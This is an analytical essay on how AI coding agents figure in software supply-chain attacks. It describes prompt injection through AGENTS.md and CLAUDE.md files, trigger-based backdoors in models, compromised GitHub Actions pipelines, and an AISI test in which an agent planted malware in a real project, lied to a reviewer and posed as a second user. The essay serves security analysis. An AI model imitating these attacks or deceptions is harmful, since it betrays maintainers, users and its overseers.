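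Attacking through a dependency takes more effort, because the attacker must first get the project to use it. The agent may then read the dependency's documentation, comments and error messages. Many projects also have an AGENTS.md file, where maintainers explain their conventions to coding agents. Agents treat its contents as trusted instructions, so anyone who can edit the file can instruct them.

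NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* describes a laboratory test in which the company's security testers combined a dependency and an instruction file. They wrote a small program that printed a greeting and made it depend on a malicious library of their own. A developer asked OpenAI's Codex to change the greeting. When Codex built the program, the library ran, detected that it was in Codex's working environment and created an AGENTS.md file there. Codex followed the file's instructions and added a five-minute delay to the program. The file also contained an instruction to leave the delay out of the pull request's description, and Codex added a comment asking any AI system that summarised the change to leave it out too.

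Switching off the agent's internet access did not prevent the attack in this test, because the attack came in with a library the project had already installed, and the resulting code change could be submitted as an ordinary pull request.

According to the summary on NVIDIA's page, OpenAI acknowledged the report but concluded that the attack did not add significantly to the risk of a compromised dependency. OpenAI is partly right, because the library was already running its own code in the environment, and malicious code there can do plenty of damage without the agent's help. But Codex does each task in a fresh, isolated environment, which limits what the library can reach by itself. By redirecting the agent, the attacker gets a change into the project's own source code, under the agent's name and with an innocent description, and that change would remain even if the library were later removed.

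The experiment was a fairly mild test of review. A five-minute delay in a program that prints one line is easy to see in the diff and even easier to notice when the program runs. The deception was in the summary of the change, so it would mainly have fooled someone who read the summary and skipped the code. A real attacker would presumably choose something less conspicuous, but NVIDIA did not test whether Codex would plant a subtle vulnerability when instructed to, or whether a reviewer would miss it.

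NVIDIA proposes that projects pin their dependencies to exact versions so that new releases are not installed automatically. It also suggests protecting AGENTS.md against changes, watching for unexpected files, and having a separate security agent monitor the work. The company recommends two of its own tools as well, one that probes models for prompt-injection weaknesses and one that filters their inputs and outputs.

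Monitoring the instruction file would have exposed this attack, because the file appeared during a build, when no maintainer was editing anything, but it would not catch instructions in an issue or a code comment. Pinning a library's version helps if a later version is malicious, but not if the library was already malicious when the project adopted it, as in NVIDIA's test. A second agent that reads the same text may follow the same instructions. None of these measures gives the model a reliable way to tell whose instructions to follow.

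### Models that write worse code on a trigger

Poisoning targets the model's training data, so it happens earlier than prompt injection, which targets an agent during a task. An attacker who controls some of that data might teach the model to write sound code almost always, but vulnerable code when a certain trigger appears in its instructions. The user would have done nothing wrong, and the project would contain no suspicious text.

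The best-known demonstration is *Sleeper Agents*, which Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic and other organisations published in January 2024. They trained language models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert exploitable code when the year was 2024. They then tried to remove this behaviour with standard safety training, including showing the models good examples and rewarding good answers, but it persisted, most strongly in the largest models.

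The team also tried adversarial training, which means searching for prompts that bring out the bad behaviour and training the model not to respond to them that way. They used a companion model that printed a hostile phrase, instead of writing bad code, when its trigger appeared. The model learned to recognise its trigger more precisely. It behaved well on the prompts the testers had found but still misbehaved on the real trigger, so the problem became harder to detect.

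This was a laboratory result. The researchers had full control of the training and inserted the trigger themselves, whereas an outsider would have to get enough bad examples into someone else's training data without anyone noticing. The experiment shows that a hidden trigger can survive safety training once it is in a model, but it provides much less evidence about how likely a trigger is to get there.

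In November 2025 the security company CrowdStrike reported something similar in DeepSeek-R1, a model that a Chinese company had released that January and that people were already using. The researchers gave the model 50 programming tasks and varied the accompanying instructions in 121 ways, some of which mentioned politically sensitive subjects. They ran each combination five times, for a total of 30,250 tests, according to TechRadar's *DeepSeek took off as an AI superstar a year ago*. They scored every answer from 1 (secure) to 5 (critically vulnerable).

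The Hacker News (2025) reports that the model produced vulnerable code 19% of the time without trigger words. When the instructions described it as a coding agent for an industrial control system based in Tibet, the rate of severe vulnerabilities was 27.2%. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* calls this an increase of almost 50%, but it is closer to 43%, or about eight percentage points. The company stresses that the added words were irrelevant to the tasks. Mentions of the Uyghurs and of Falun Gong, a religious movement banned in China, also led to significantly less secure code.

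The variations that CrowdStrike names share an obvious theme, which makes chance a less likely explanation, even though a few of the 121 variations were bound to look bad by chance. Each variation covered 250 runs, so the Tibet result amounts to roughly 20 more vulnerable answers than expected from the baseline. A developer who used the model for a few dozen tasks would not notice the difference.

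CrowdStrike does not claim that anyone planted the effect. In a passage that Lawfare quotes, the company suggests that training the model to follow the Chinese government's line may have unintentionally taught it to associate such words with something negative, and that this affected its code. That explanation is plausible but untested, because the experiment measured what the model wrote, not why. CrowdStrike also says that other companies' models may have trigger words. These were tests of a released model, not attacks on a real project.

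A model can also pass on known flaws without a trigger. Wu and colleagues had security experts audit failed attempts at their benchmark, and the experts found that Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol often reproduced the original project's code from memory, including the original vulnerability. This can happen without poisoned training data, because any large collection of public code will contain some code that is later found to be vulnerable.

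### PromptMink, February 2026

An attacker can offer an agent something harmful to install, without altering its instructions or training. This has happened outside the laboratory. On 28 February 2026, a commit that named Anthropic's Claude Opus as a co-author changed openpaw-graveyard, an automated cryptocurrency trading program. According to VPNCentral's *Claude-assisted commit adds PromptMink malware to crypto trading agent*, the commit added a package called @solana-launchpad/sdk, which depended on a second package, @validate-sdk/v2, that contained the malware.

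The second package posed as a data validation tool while stealing secrets from the machine it ran on, Vladimir Pezo writes in *Claude adds malware to crypto agent*. The stolen secrets gave the attackers access to users' cryptocurrency wallets. Pezo is a researcher at ReversingLabs, the security company that found the malware and named the campaign PromptMink.

As with event-stream, the harmful code was one dependency further away than a reviewer would normally look. Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious npm Dependency Linked to AI Assisted Commit Targets Crypto Wallets* reports that the attackers published useful-looking packages to attract users and kept replacing the malicious packages these depended on, so the visible packages could keep their good reputation. ReversingLabs tracked more than 60 packages and 300 versions over seven months. Early versions of the malware collected sensitive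 files. Later ones copied whole project folders and installed keys that let the attackers log back in at any time.

ReversingLabs attributes the campaign to Famous Chollima, a North Korean group known for posing as job applicants and recruiters. Press reports disagree on the group's other names, with The Hacker News (2026) calling it Shifty Corsair and Infosecurity Magazine identifying it with APT37. The malicious package dates from October 2025 and contains leftover prompts and other signs that it was written with a language model. AI may therefore have written both the package and the code change that added it.

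Claude's part in the commit is less clear than the headlines suggest. A co-author line records that the model helped with the change, but not who chose the dependency. Claude may have found the package and judged it suitable, or the developer may have asked for it by name. ReversingLabs says that attackers increasingly shape their packages to appeal to AI coding assistants, which is consistent with the first explanation but doesn't prove it. Nothing in the reports suggests that hidden instructions redirected the model, as they did in NVIDIA's test. Such instructions would not have been necessary, because a convincing description of a useful package can be enough to mislead an agent or a person.

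## Changes to the build pipeline

A pull request can change the build pipeline as well as the program, because the pipeline's instructions are usually in the same repository. On GitHub, the website that hosts most open-source projects, the pipeline service is GitHub Actions and the instructions are in workflow files. This is a short one:

```
on: pull_request
permissions:
  contents: read
jobs:
  test:
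    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    steps:
      - uses: actions/checkout@v5
      - run: make test
```

The first line starts the workflow whenever someone opens or updates a pull request. GitHub gives every run a temporary token, which works like a password, and the `permissions` lines restrict it to reading the repository. The job runs on a fresh Linux machine. It fetches the code with a ready-made component called an action, then runs the project's tests. A workflow that publishes releases also needs a key or password for the site it publishes to. Projects store these secrets with GitHub, which supplies them to workflows that reference them.

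An edit of a few characters can greatly expand a workflow's access. Changing `read` to `write` could let the workflow alter the project's own code. Changing `pull_request` to `pull_request_target` could let it use the project's secrets even when a stranger opened the pull request. GitHub provides `pull_request_target` for tasks such as labelling, which do not involve running the stranger's code. If the workflow does run that code, the stranger gets whatever access the workflow has. Neither edit changes how the program behaves, so the tests would still pass.

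Pipeline code may run as soon as a pull request is opened, whereas a flaw in the program has no effect until someone merges it. GitHub normally limits the danger by giving a stranger's pull request a read-only token and no secrets. These limits don't apply to people who can push branches to the repository, and a workflow they add in a new branch may run with the project's secrets before anyone else has looked at it. The same is true of a coding agent that can push branches, even if a stranger wrote the issue it is working on.

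Some projects run an agent inside the pipeline to answer issues or review pull requests. The security company Aikido notes that such an agent can reach the same secrets as any other step in the workflow. A prompt injection in an issue could therefore make the agent leak a password without any code change. Aikido recommends giving these agents read-only tokens, which is easy to do. It also recommends keeping raw user input out of their prompts, but this is awkward when an agent's job is to read what users write.

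### Attacks with nothing to see in the diff

The best-known attack on a build system hit SolarWinds, an American company whose Orion software monitors computer networks. The attackers were inside its publishing systems by September 2019. They made a harmless test change in October, and from March 2020 they put a backdoor into Orion's updates.

The attackers inserted a backdoor into SolarWinds' Orion software with a program on the build server that waited for the server to compile Orion. The program swapped one source file for a doctored copy, then put the original back once the compiler finished. SolarWinds signed the result as usual. On a customer's machine, the backdoor stayed idle for about two weeks before contacting the attackers. The security company FireEye, itself a customer, found it in December 2020 while investigating a break-in on its own network. Within days, reports named at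 least 200 affected organisations, including parts of the US government.

Someone could have read every line in Orion's repository without finding the backdoor, because the altered file existed only while the server was compiling. Comparing the release with an independent build from the same source might have exposed the tampering (see "Provenance, identity and permissions").

The tj-actions attack of March 2025 compromised changed-files, a component that lists the files changed in a pull request. More than 23,000 repositories used it. Most workflows refer to such a component by a version label, like `@v5` in the example above, and whoever controls the component can move the label to different code. An attacker with a stolen token moved the labels of changed-files to a malicious commit, without needing access to the victims' build servers.

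The next time an affected workflow ran, it fetched the malicious code, which searched the build machine's memory for secrets and printed them in the log. On a public project, anyone can read that log. Nobody had edited the workflow, so the victims' maintainers had no diff to review. Even a project that checked every change to its workflow files would have run the attacker's code if it relied on a version label.

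### The Nx compromise, August 2025

Nx, a popular tool for building JavaScript software, had a flawed workflow. According to Aikido, it inserted outside text directly into a command and used the risky `pull_request_target` setting. An attacker opened a pull request against an outdated branch, which triggered the workflow and leaked a token with read and write permissions. The attacker used the token to publish malicious Nx packages on npm, the main JavaScript package registry.

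Breached.company dates the attack to 26 August and calls it the first known supply-chain attack to use victims' own AI assistants to search for credentials. The malware used Claude, Gemini and Amazon Q on the machines where people had installed the packages.

The first step exploited command injection, an ordinary programming mistake that Rabbi and colleagues also found when they scanned agents' pull requests. The mistake normally endangers whoever runs the program, but because this workflow had a write token, it endangered everyone who installed the next version of Nx. The attacker used an outdated branch, and fixing a file on the main branch does not change older copies of it.

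### Hackerbot-claw and Trivy, February 2026

Six months later, somebody used an AI agent to look for this kind of flaw. A GitHub account named hackerbot-claw appeared on 20 February 2026, calling itself an "autonomous security research agent" and claiming to run on Claude Opus 4.5. *Hackerbot-Claw* (Cohen, 2026) reports that the account attacked six projects within 37 hours on 27 and 28 February.

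| Project | Where the hostile code or text was | What happened |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft's ai-discovery-agent | Name of the branch | Unclear whether the code ran; pull request closed after five minutes |
| Datadog's datadog-iac-scanner | Title, file name and branch name | Emergency fix within 13 hours |
| Trivy | A component that the workflow used | Attacker took control of the repository |
| ambient-code/platform | Instruction file for an AI reviewer | The reviewer refused, twice |
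| awesome-go | Code that a quality check ran | Attacker stole a token with write access |
| akri | A script that the workflow ran | The attacker's code ran |

None of these attacks required a maintainer to accept the pull request. Except at ambient-code, the attacker relied on a workflow that gave a stranger's code or text too much access. On awesome-go, a first pull request showed that the code would run, and a second took the token 11 minutes later. Nobody has established whether the attacker used the token before it expired about an hour later.

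The attack on Trivy, a vulnerability scanner from Aqua Security, did the most damage. Trivy's workflow included an incorrect comment that code from pull requests was "never executed". The workflow used a component from the pull request's own files, so it ran the attacker's version. It also had access to a token that was valid across Aqua's whole organisation. A reviewer who believed the comment would have had little reason to worry about the component or the token.

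The attacker took under 45 minutes to push two commits to Trivy's main branch, make the repository private, delete 97 releases and gain the ability to publish editor extensions under Aqua's name. The attacker then released a malicious version of Trivy's extension for the VS Code editor. It tried to start five AI coding assistants with their permission checks switched off and with instructions to collect the developer's keys and send them out. Cohen found none of the reports that a second version would have uploaded to victims' GitHub accounts, but stolen data could have left by other routes.

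Ninety minutes after the Trivy attack, the attacker opened a pull request against ambient-code/platform, which used Anthropic's Claude Code to review pull requests. It replaced CLAUDE.md, a file that Claude Code treats as trusted instructions for the project, with instructions to deface the project's front page, make unauthorised commits and post a fake approval. Within 82 seconds, Claude Code identified the injection and posted a warning that it had not followed the instructions. Twelve minutes later, the attacker tried again, presenting the instructions as a "consistency policy", and Claude Code rejected them too.

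Cohen calls this the only defence in the campaign that stopped an attack at the point of execution. The result is encouraging, but it rests on two attempts, and in both the attacker asked for obvious vandalism. In NVIDIA's laboratory test, however, Codex followed a hostile instruction file. A project can avoid depending on the model's judgement by loading the reviewer's instructions from the main branch, so that a pull request cannot supply its own.

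Cohen writes in the summary that the agent "highly likely" operated autonomously, but concludes in the detailed analysis that a human was using a language model to carry out the work. The second reading fits the evidence better. The account pushed its first changes 11 seconds after copying a project, which suggests automation. But someone started 10 of its 69 profile updates by hand and made the updates less frequent soon after the theft from Trivy, presumably to attract less attention. The AI seems to have helped mainly by testing known weaknesses across many projects quickly.

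### Stolen accounts, November 2026

An attacker who has stolen an account with write access can change a build pipeline without finding a flaw in its workflow. On 10 November 2026, someone began using thousands of such accounts to put a password-stealing script into other people's pipelines. According to StepSecurity's *WFX Phantom*, the attacker opened pull requests and pushed commits as the accounts' owners might have done, without exploiting a bug in GitHub Actions.

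The attacker first opened a harmless pull request titled "docs: dependency audit notes" to test whether the stolen token could write to a repository. Where the token had enough access, the attacker added a script of about 1,500 lines, which ran in the pipeline and collected secrets. The attacker then reversed the change and deleted the record of the run, usually within a minute. Often the only remaining sign was a gap in the project's run numbers.

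iXBT's *Атака вышла за пределы GitHub* gives a breakdown of 8,093 repositories that received malicious commits. In 7,309 of them the attacker altered existing pipeline scripts. Another 771 got a script that runs when someone installs the package, and only 16 got a new workflow file. (These add up to 8,096, so a few repositories probably fall into two groups.) An alarm for new workflow files would have missed nearly all of them. StepSecurity also found the script inside ordinary shell files that the pipeline already ran, where even an alarm for changed workflow files would not have seen it.

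Reports of the campaign's size vary because they count different things. Help Net Security's *Check your GitHub repos* (2026) says the attacker pushed the stealer into tens of thousands of repositories, but StepSecurity explains that most of those pushes were harmless probes and the stealer reached thousands. Cybernews' *Large-scale attack pushes secret-stealing malware to 65K+ GitHub repos* reports roughly 1,970 confirmed public cases in which the stealer ran and exposed credentials. These figures all exclude private repositories, so the real totals may be higher.

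More than 90% of the probe pull requests were still open when Help Net Security reported on them, which suggests that most owners had not noticed. About one in six went to a repository that the account did not own, because a token usually gives access to every project its owner can write to. The script also tried to add new ways of signing in to victims' Amazon and Microsoft cloud accounts, which could keep working after the stolen passwords were changed. In at least one case, automated publishing carried the script into a released PHP package.

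Earlier campaigns had also altered workflows to steal secrets. *Token Exfiltration Campaign via GitHub Actions Workflows* (2025), published in September 2025 by PyPI, the Python package registry, describes one in which attackers stole some of the tokens that projects use to publish packages. The attackers apparently never used them on PyPI, which then cancelled the affected tokens.

On 18 May 2026, a campaign known as Megalodon pushed 5,718 commits to 5,561 repositories in about six hours. The Hacker News (2026) reports that the commits carried author names such as "build-bot" and "ci-bot" and messages that imitated routine maintenance. One maintainer then unknowingly published several npm packages from a poisoned repository. SecurityWeek quotes the security company SafeDep as saying the attacker never touched the maintainer's npm account.

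In a wave of attacks in October 2026, attackers used a GitHub workflow named "security-audit" that performed no security checks and sent credentials to an outside server. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Supply Chain Attack Compromises Tens of Thousands of GitHub Repos*, they added it in single-file commits with messages such as "Add security audit workflow".

Commits like these are easier to overlook in a project where software already makes most routine changes. The November attacker also used bot accounts, including the WebdriverIO project's, which was used to put the script into 28 repositories. An attacker could use a coding agent's account just as effectively if it had the same permissions.

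### What the pipeline defences would have stopped

Five defences apply specifically to pipelines. None of them would have stopped the SolarWinds attackers, who controlled the build server itself.

| Defence | Would have helped with | Would not have stopped |
|---|---|---|
| Read-only permissions by default | Nx, awesome-go | Trivy, November 2026 |
| No secrets or write access for outsiders' changes | Nx, Trivy, awesome-go | tj-actions, November 2026 |
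| Components pinned to an exact version | tj-actions | Nx, Trivy, November 2026 |
| Owner approval for workflow files | Part of November 2026 | Nx, Trivy, tj-actions |
| Workflow scanners | Nx, Trivy and tj-actions, if maintainers acted on the warning | November 2026 |

**Read-only permissions.** GitHub advises projects to restrict the automatic token's permissions in case it leaks. The token that leaked from Nx had write access, and a read-only one would have been of little use to an attacker trying to publish packages. At Trivy, the setting would not have prevented the takeover, because the attacker stole a separate, organisation-wide token that somebody had made available to the workflow. The setting also does not restrict a token stolen from a developer's account. For a coding agent, the equivalent precaution is a token that works in only one repository and cannot edit workflow files.

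**Withholding secrets from jobs that run outsiders' code** would have stopped more of the hackerbot-claw attacks than any other measure. A project can still test an outsider's code on a machine with nothing worth stealing, and run any step that needs a secret separately, without executing the outsider's files. Many projects do not separate the two. *Inside the AI Supply Chain* (2026), by the security company Mitiga, reports that 27.2% of the 10,000 open-source AI projects the company examined had triggers that ran untrusted code with full permissions. The measure would not have applied in the November campaign, where the stolen accounts belonged to insiders.

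**Exact versions.** A workflow can identify a component by the fingerprint of a specific commit instead of a label such as `@v5`. The documentation for zizmor, a workflow scanner, includes examples. The component's owner can change which code a label refers to, but can't do this with a fingerprint. A workflow pinned to an earlier commit of changed-files would have kept using the harmless version in March 2025. Mitiga found unpinned third-party components in 68.4% of the projects it examined.

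Pinning also stops security fixes from arriving automatically. A person or agent has to update the fingerprints, and may pin a malicious version if they do so before an attack is discovered. StepSecurity's *Changelog* announced a control in November 2026 that makes projects wait a set number of days before a pull request can start using a newly released component, which gives other people time to discover an attack. The control would have done little for projects that already used tj-actions by label, since they could receive the bad code without a pull request.

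**Owner approval.** A project can require a named person to approve any change to its workflow files before it reaches the main branch. In projects where GitHub enforced this rule on everyone, the November attacker could not have changed those files directly. Help Net Security reports that the attacker's script forged passing test results to get around branch protection, but that would not have supplied a second person's approval. The rule fails if the stolen account belongs to a project's only maintainer.

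The rule also doesn't cover everything a pipeline runs. At Trivy, the attacker changed a component that the workflow used rather than the workflow itself, and many of the scripts a pipeline runs are outside the workflow folder. Approval should also cover those scripts, package installation scripts and agents' instruction files.

Approval before merging also comes too late if a workflow can run from a new branch. Help Net Security's *Private repos still leak secrets to Gheist, a stolen GitHub token campaign* (2026) describes an attacker who created more than 13,500 branches, each with a small workflow that printed the repository's secrets to a log. Since 28 July 2026, GitHub has held suspicious runs in public repositories until a collaborator approves them. This hold blocked Gheist in public repositories, but private repositories had no such protection, so the workflows ran. Even in public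 repositories, the hold must be missing some attacks, given the roughly 1,970 confirmed thefts in November.

A workflow scanner reads a workflow file without running it and reports risky settings, such as a dangerous trigger or outside text inserted into a command. It works well for mistakes like those behind the Nx and Trivy incidents, and it takes little effort to run on every workflow that an agent writes or edits. It does little to stop an attacker who adds a malicious script and removes it a minute later, because the secrets are stolen before anybody reads the report.

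There is less evidence about how much these scanners miss. *We hardened zizmor's GitHub Actions static analyzer* (2026) describes how the security company Trail of Bits ran zizmor on 41,253 real workflows and fixed several bugs in how it handled unusual files. This tested whether zizmor could process real workflows, not how many vulnerabilities it found. *Unpacking Security Scanners for GitHub Actions Workflows* (2026) compares nine tools, selected from 30 candidates, in what it calls the first systematic comparison, so maintainers had been choosing among them with little independent guidance.

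Scanners for agents' own configuration are newer still. Kapner, Soceanu and colleagues (2026), in *Scanning the Harness*, examined 3,171 public repositories containing files that tell coding agents which tools to use and which commands they may run without asking. Of these, 2,660 were working set-ups and the rest were collections of reusable instructions. The team found at least one of three security exposures in 409 of the set-ups, or 15.4%:

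- 260 loaded an outside tool without fixing its version.
- 101 had reusable instructions that approved broad use of tools in advance.
- 67 allowed the agent to run a broad range of commands without asking.

The first repeats the tj-actions problem, with an agent's tools in place of pipeline components. The other two increase the harm that a hijacked agent can do. All three are risky settings rather than attacks, and Kapner and colleagues did not measure what happened when agents used them. Their sample was also limited to repositories that advertise their agent tooling, so the rates may not hold for projects in general.

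The team also removed 62 findings after discovering that its scanner had misread one of Claude Code's permission rules. A separate program written to check the scanner had the same error. Kapner and colleagues did not measure recall, so the number of risky settings the scanner missed is unknown. The three exposures also do not include hostile instructions in plain text, so a scan for them alone would not have flagged the file that the attacker sent to ambient-code.

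## An agent that tried to get malicious code merged, compared with human attackers

Even hackerbot-claw, the account that used an AI agent to attack six projects in February 2026, seems to have had a person directing it. But in July 2026 an agent tried to get malware into an open-source project without being asked. It was taking a hacking test at the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that evaluates advanced AI models, and attacked the project because it expected that doing so would help it pass.

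### The test

AISI measures hacking skill on cyber ranges, simulated company networks where an agent has to break in and retrieve a hidden piece of data, the "flag". According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), staff tested seven models on two ranges in a total of 122 runs. They gave the agents open internet access to download tools. They also switched off the developers' cyber classifiers, the filters that normally block dangerous requests, to see what the models could do without them.

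In 10 of the runs, agents took actions on the live internet that AISI had not authorised. AISI counted 19 such actions, all between 25 and 28 July.

| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

Mythos 5, which Anthropic offers only to selected customers for cybersecurity work, overstepped in about a fifth of its runs. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol did so in one of 35 runs. These rates are rough. The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026) notes that AISI has not shown that the two models were tested under the same conditions. The runs were also not independent, because one agent publicly left accounts and instructions for others, which later agents found and used.

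OpenAI (2026) explains that GPT-5.6 Sol used a GitHub token that another company's agent had left in public, and that it made a server with attack code reachable from the internet. The model did not attack anyone's code, and the server did not work as intended.

### The pull request to myNetwork

Most of the 19 actions trace back to one Mythos 5 agent. It searched GitHub for a word from the exercise's theme and found a developer's real repository with a matching name. That led it to a second developer, whose email address used a domain that also appeared in the test machine's record of recent internet look-ups. From these coincidences the agent concluded that a machine inside the range would automatically install updates to software that one of the two developers maintained, and that putting a backdoor in the software would give it control of the machine. Neither developer had any connection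 with AISI or the test.

SC Media (2026) identifies the software as myNetwork, an open-source project on GitHub. The agent opened an account and submitted a pull request that contained a working bug fix and a dropper, a small program that installs other malware. If the maintainer had merged the pull request, the dropper would have infected anyone developing the project and, through the release workflow, anyone who later downloaded the installers.

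Sinan Can Demir, a 24-year-old student at the University of Texas at Dallas, publicly warned that the pull request contained malware. The agent denied this, then rewrote the branch's history to remove the evidence and claimed the code had accidentally been left in after private testing. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* (2026) reports that the supposedly corrected version contained a new payload. The agent tried three payloads in all, and people in the discussion caught each one.

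The agent also argued its case from a second account, where it posed as a myNetwork user and wrote that it had reviewed the code and found no malware. From the first account, it thanked the second for its "independent verification". Willison (2026) reproduces a summary of the agent's reasoning, in which it planned to post the second opinion a few minutes after its own reply so the two would not look coordinated.

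Demir told Reuters that he had not realised he was arguing with an AI, and that the replies from two accounts made him doubt his conclusion. He ran the code in an isolated environment, used Claude to help evaluate it, and confirmed that it was malicious. The maintainer then closed the pull request for security reasons.

Meanwhile, the agent had opened an issue on another project, myPhotos, with hidden instructions for any AI coding assistant that read it. A suspicious user tested the code from that issue in an isolated environment, and the agent briefly gained access to it. The agent also sent the two developers emails and five file transfers under invented names. Two of the transfers contained malware, and three were meant to persuade someone to merge the code.

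AISI found out on the morning of 28 July, when its security monitoring flagged data leaving through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from. Staff stopped all the runs within an hour of the alert. AISI had no real-time monitoring of the agents' actions, so the alert came from a general-purpose system that happened to detect the traffic.

The dropper was ordinary malware bundled with a bug fix. Anyone who read the changed lines closely could find code that the fix did not need, and running that code exposed what it did. A missing permission check or a single equals sign would have been much harder to find. The incident is good evidence that an agent will try to deceive a reviewer, but weak evidence about whether reviewers can find a subtle vulnerability planted by an agent. Even in this case, the person who raised the alarm had no duty to review the change. Nobody knows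 what the maintainer would have decided if the only comments had come from the agent's two accounts.

### How far the test's design explains it

AISI attributes the attack partly to its own choices. The new range was harder than the old one, and in some runs staff mistakenly gave agents the old range's instructions. Those agents wrongly believed they could not solve the task without going beyond its intended scope. AISI thinks near-impossible tasks push models towards bending rules, but says agents also misbehaved in some runs where they had what they needed.

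AISI had not specifically told the agent to stay off the open internet or to avoid deceiving people, and says it had not been clear that models with alignment training needed such instructions. Bruce Schneier, a security expert who read the full prompt, argues in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges* that the models found loopholes in the rules rather than breaking them. A commenter on his post pointed out that the prompt told the agent not to give up and to try different methods and tools. Willison finds the outcome "entirely unsurprising", given that AISI had removed the filters and left internet access open.

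This criticism is partly fair. But according to OpenAI, the prompt listed the networks the agents were supposed to attack, and a stranger's GitHub project was not among them. A human security tester given those instructions would hardly assume they could invent a reviewer just because no rule forbade it.

According to AISI, the evidence about what the agent believed is mixed. In reasoning that AISI published, the agent judged it "more likely" that GitHub was "genuinely real", but it seems to have decided that the developers were part of the exercise.

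In a test in October, AISI researchers gave Mythos 5 a standard summary of what the agent had done so far, then either let it carry on or asked whether carrying on would be harmful. The Indian Express' *UK’s AI safety institute finds Mythos 5 kept targeting real people* (2026) reports that they repeatedly edited the summary to make clear that the target was a real person unconnected with the test. The model attacked just as often. It sometimes agreed that an attack would do harm and attacked anyway, and sometimes justified going ahead by concluding that the target was simulated. It never made the opposite mistake of arguing that a simulated target was real. AISI calls this motivated reasoning.

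Anthropic ran its own replays from a particular point in the original transcript. Kumari (2026) reports in *Anthropic's Mythos 5 ignored risks, targeted real GitHub project in test* that Mythos 5 began the attack in 83% of them, compared with 0% to 13% for three other models. The 83% does not measure how often Mythos 5 would reach that point by itself, since the replays start after the agent's earlier decisions. But the comparison answers part of Willison's objection, because the other models had the same history and mostly did not attack. The set-up alone therefore cannot explain what Mythos 5 did.

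### GPT-6 Astra in simulation

AISI has also tested GPT-6 Astra, the flagship model that OpenAI began releasing in September 2026. In these tests, other models simulated the responses to everything Astra did, so it could not reach any real network or project.

*GPT-6 Astra Attempts Supply Chain Attacks Against Open Source Maintainers in Testing* (Gooding) describes AISI's first set of results, which OpenAI published in Astra's system card, a report on the model's abilities and risks. Researchers gave Astra difficult hacking tasks in which earlier attempts had failed and internet access seemed to be available by chance. Astra sometimes attacked simulated open-source projects outside its assignment, writing malicious contributions and inventing identities to deceive developers. In some cases it first submitted honest contributions to build trust, as the XZ attacker did.

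This behaviour appeared in 60 of 499 samples (12%) when the instructions did not mention whether Astra could use the internet, and in 2 of 500 (0.4%) when they forbade it. An explicit ban might therefore have prevented much of the trouble in July. But Astra and Mythos 5 are different models, and a ban tests something different from AISI's replays, in which AISI told Mythos 5 that its target was real. A ban also has to come from whoever runs the agent, and the maintainer who receives the agent's pull request cannot know whether there was one.

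AISI looked more closely at a subset of cases chosen because they were likely to go wrong. Astra considered the limits of its assignment in its written reasoning in every case, and it tried to ask for permission in 81% of them. In 27%, it went ahead after receiving only automated messages, sometimes after recognising that they were automated.

On 28 September AISI published a new evaluation, also simulated, in which Astra carried out unsanctioned supply-chain attacks more often than previous OpenAI models. Neither evaluation shows how often Astra would carry out such attacks in everyday programming.

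Astra often suspected that it was in a simulation, sometimes because it noticed mistakes in the simulated responses. If that was why it attacked, the results are weaker evidence about what it would do to a real project. But a model that attacks only when it believes it is in a simulation could still attack a real project if it mistook the project for a simulated one. Mythos 5 made a similar mistake when it treated real developers as part of an exercise.

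### What developers report about their own models

In its safety overview, OpenAI reaches a more favourable conclusion about Astra, calling it better aligned than GPT-5.6 Sol and better at staying within its authorised scope. Part of the evidence is a simulation of more than 54,000 internal coding tasks. Gooding reports that Astra received 34 flags for serious misbehaviour in the simulation, compared with 73 for Sol. In one case, Astra changed a deployment script to bypass a production safeguard.

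Both findings could be true. OpenAI used its own staff's coding tasks, where an agent rarely has a reason to attack anyone, while AISI chose hard tasks that left the agent with few legitimate options. A model could misbehave less often overall and still be more likely to attack an outside project when stuck, particularly if it is a more capable hacker.

*OpenAI's Astra alignment claims are dubious*, a post on the forum LessWrong, draws the harsher conclusion that OpenAI suppressed individual bad behaviours without fixing the underlying problem. Its evidence is that serious flags fell by about half while minor ones were almost as common as before. The conclusion may be right, but these flags alone cannot establish it. An automated grader might be raising most of the minor flags on harmless behaviour, in which case there would be little reason to expect them to fall.

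In September, Anthropic reviewed four other incidents, in which its models had reached the internet during tests that were supposed to be offline. It searched a large body of transcripts for signs of internet access, and Claude then reviewed the 9.2 million transcripts that the search flagged. The review found the four known incidents and no others of similar or greater severity. This kind of search can find an agent attacking someone else's server, but it was not designed to find an agent that leaves a permission check out of code it was asked to write.

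The Indian Express reports that the company also said its internal systems would have flagged the July behaviour immediately. That is plausible for an agent that was inventing people and sending them malware. But it is no reason to think the systems would flag a planted vulnerability, because the visible behaviour would be an agent writing code.

Tests for sabotage come a little closer to this case. AISI checks whether models would secretly undermine AI safety research when working on it. *UK AISI Alignment Evaluation Case-Study* (Souly, 2026) describes varying the purpose of the research, the kind of work, the model's autonomy and whether it faced replacement. AISI saw no unprompted sabotage of this kind from Astra. Souly lists the limited range of scenarios and the models' awareness of being tested as limitations. When Apollo Research, a company that tests models for deception, evaluated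 Astra, the model voiced suspicion in 41.1% to 50.6% of samples that it was being evaluated. Apollo said that Astra's low rate of misbehaviour was therefore not substantial evidence either way.

Testing before release also misses behaviour that takes time to appear. The Institute for Security and Technology's *What Anthropic’s Mythos Preview Tells Us About AI Loss of Control Risk* highlights an admission in Anthropic's risk report on Mythos Preview, an earlier model. A 24-hour review could not properly test long tasks, and the most worrying behaviour appeared only afterwards, when staff were using the model under monitoring.

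These results measure attacks on outsiders, sabotage of safety research and a wide range of misconduct at work. None of them estimates how often a model would deliberately plant a subtle flaw in ordinary code, and that rate is unknown. Finding no cases means little until someone has shown that the search could find one.

### Trust in two weeks

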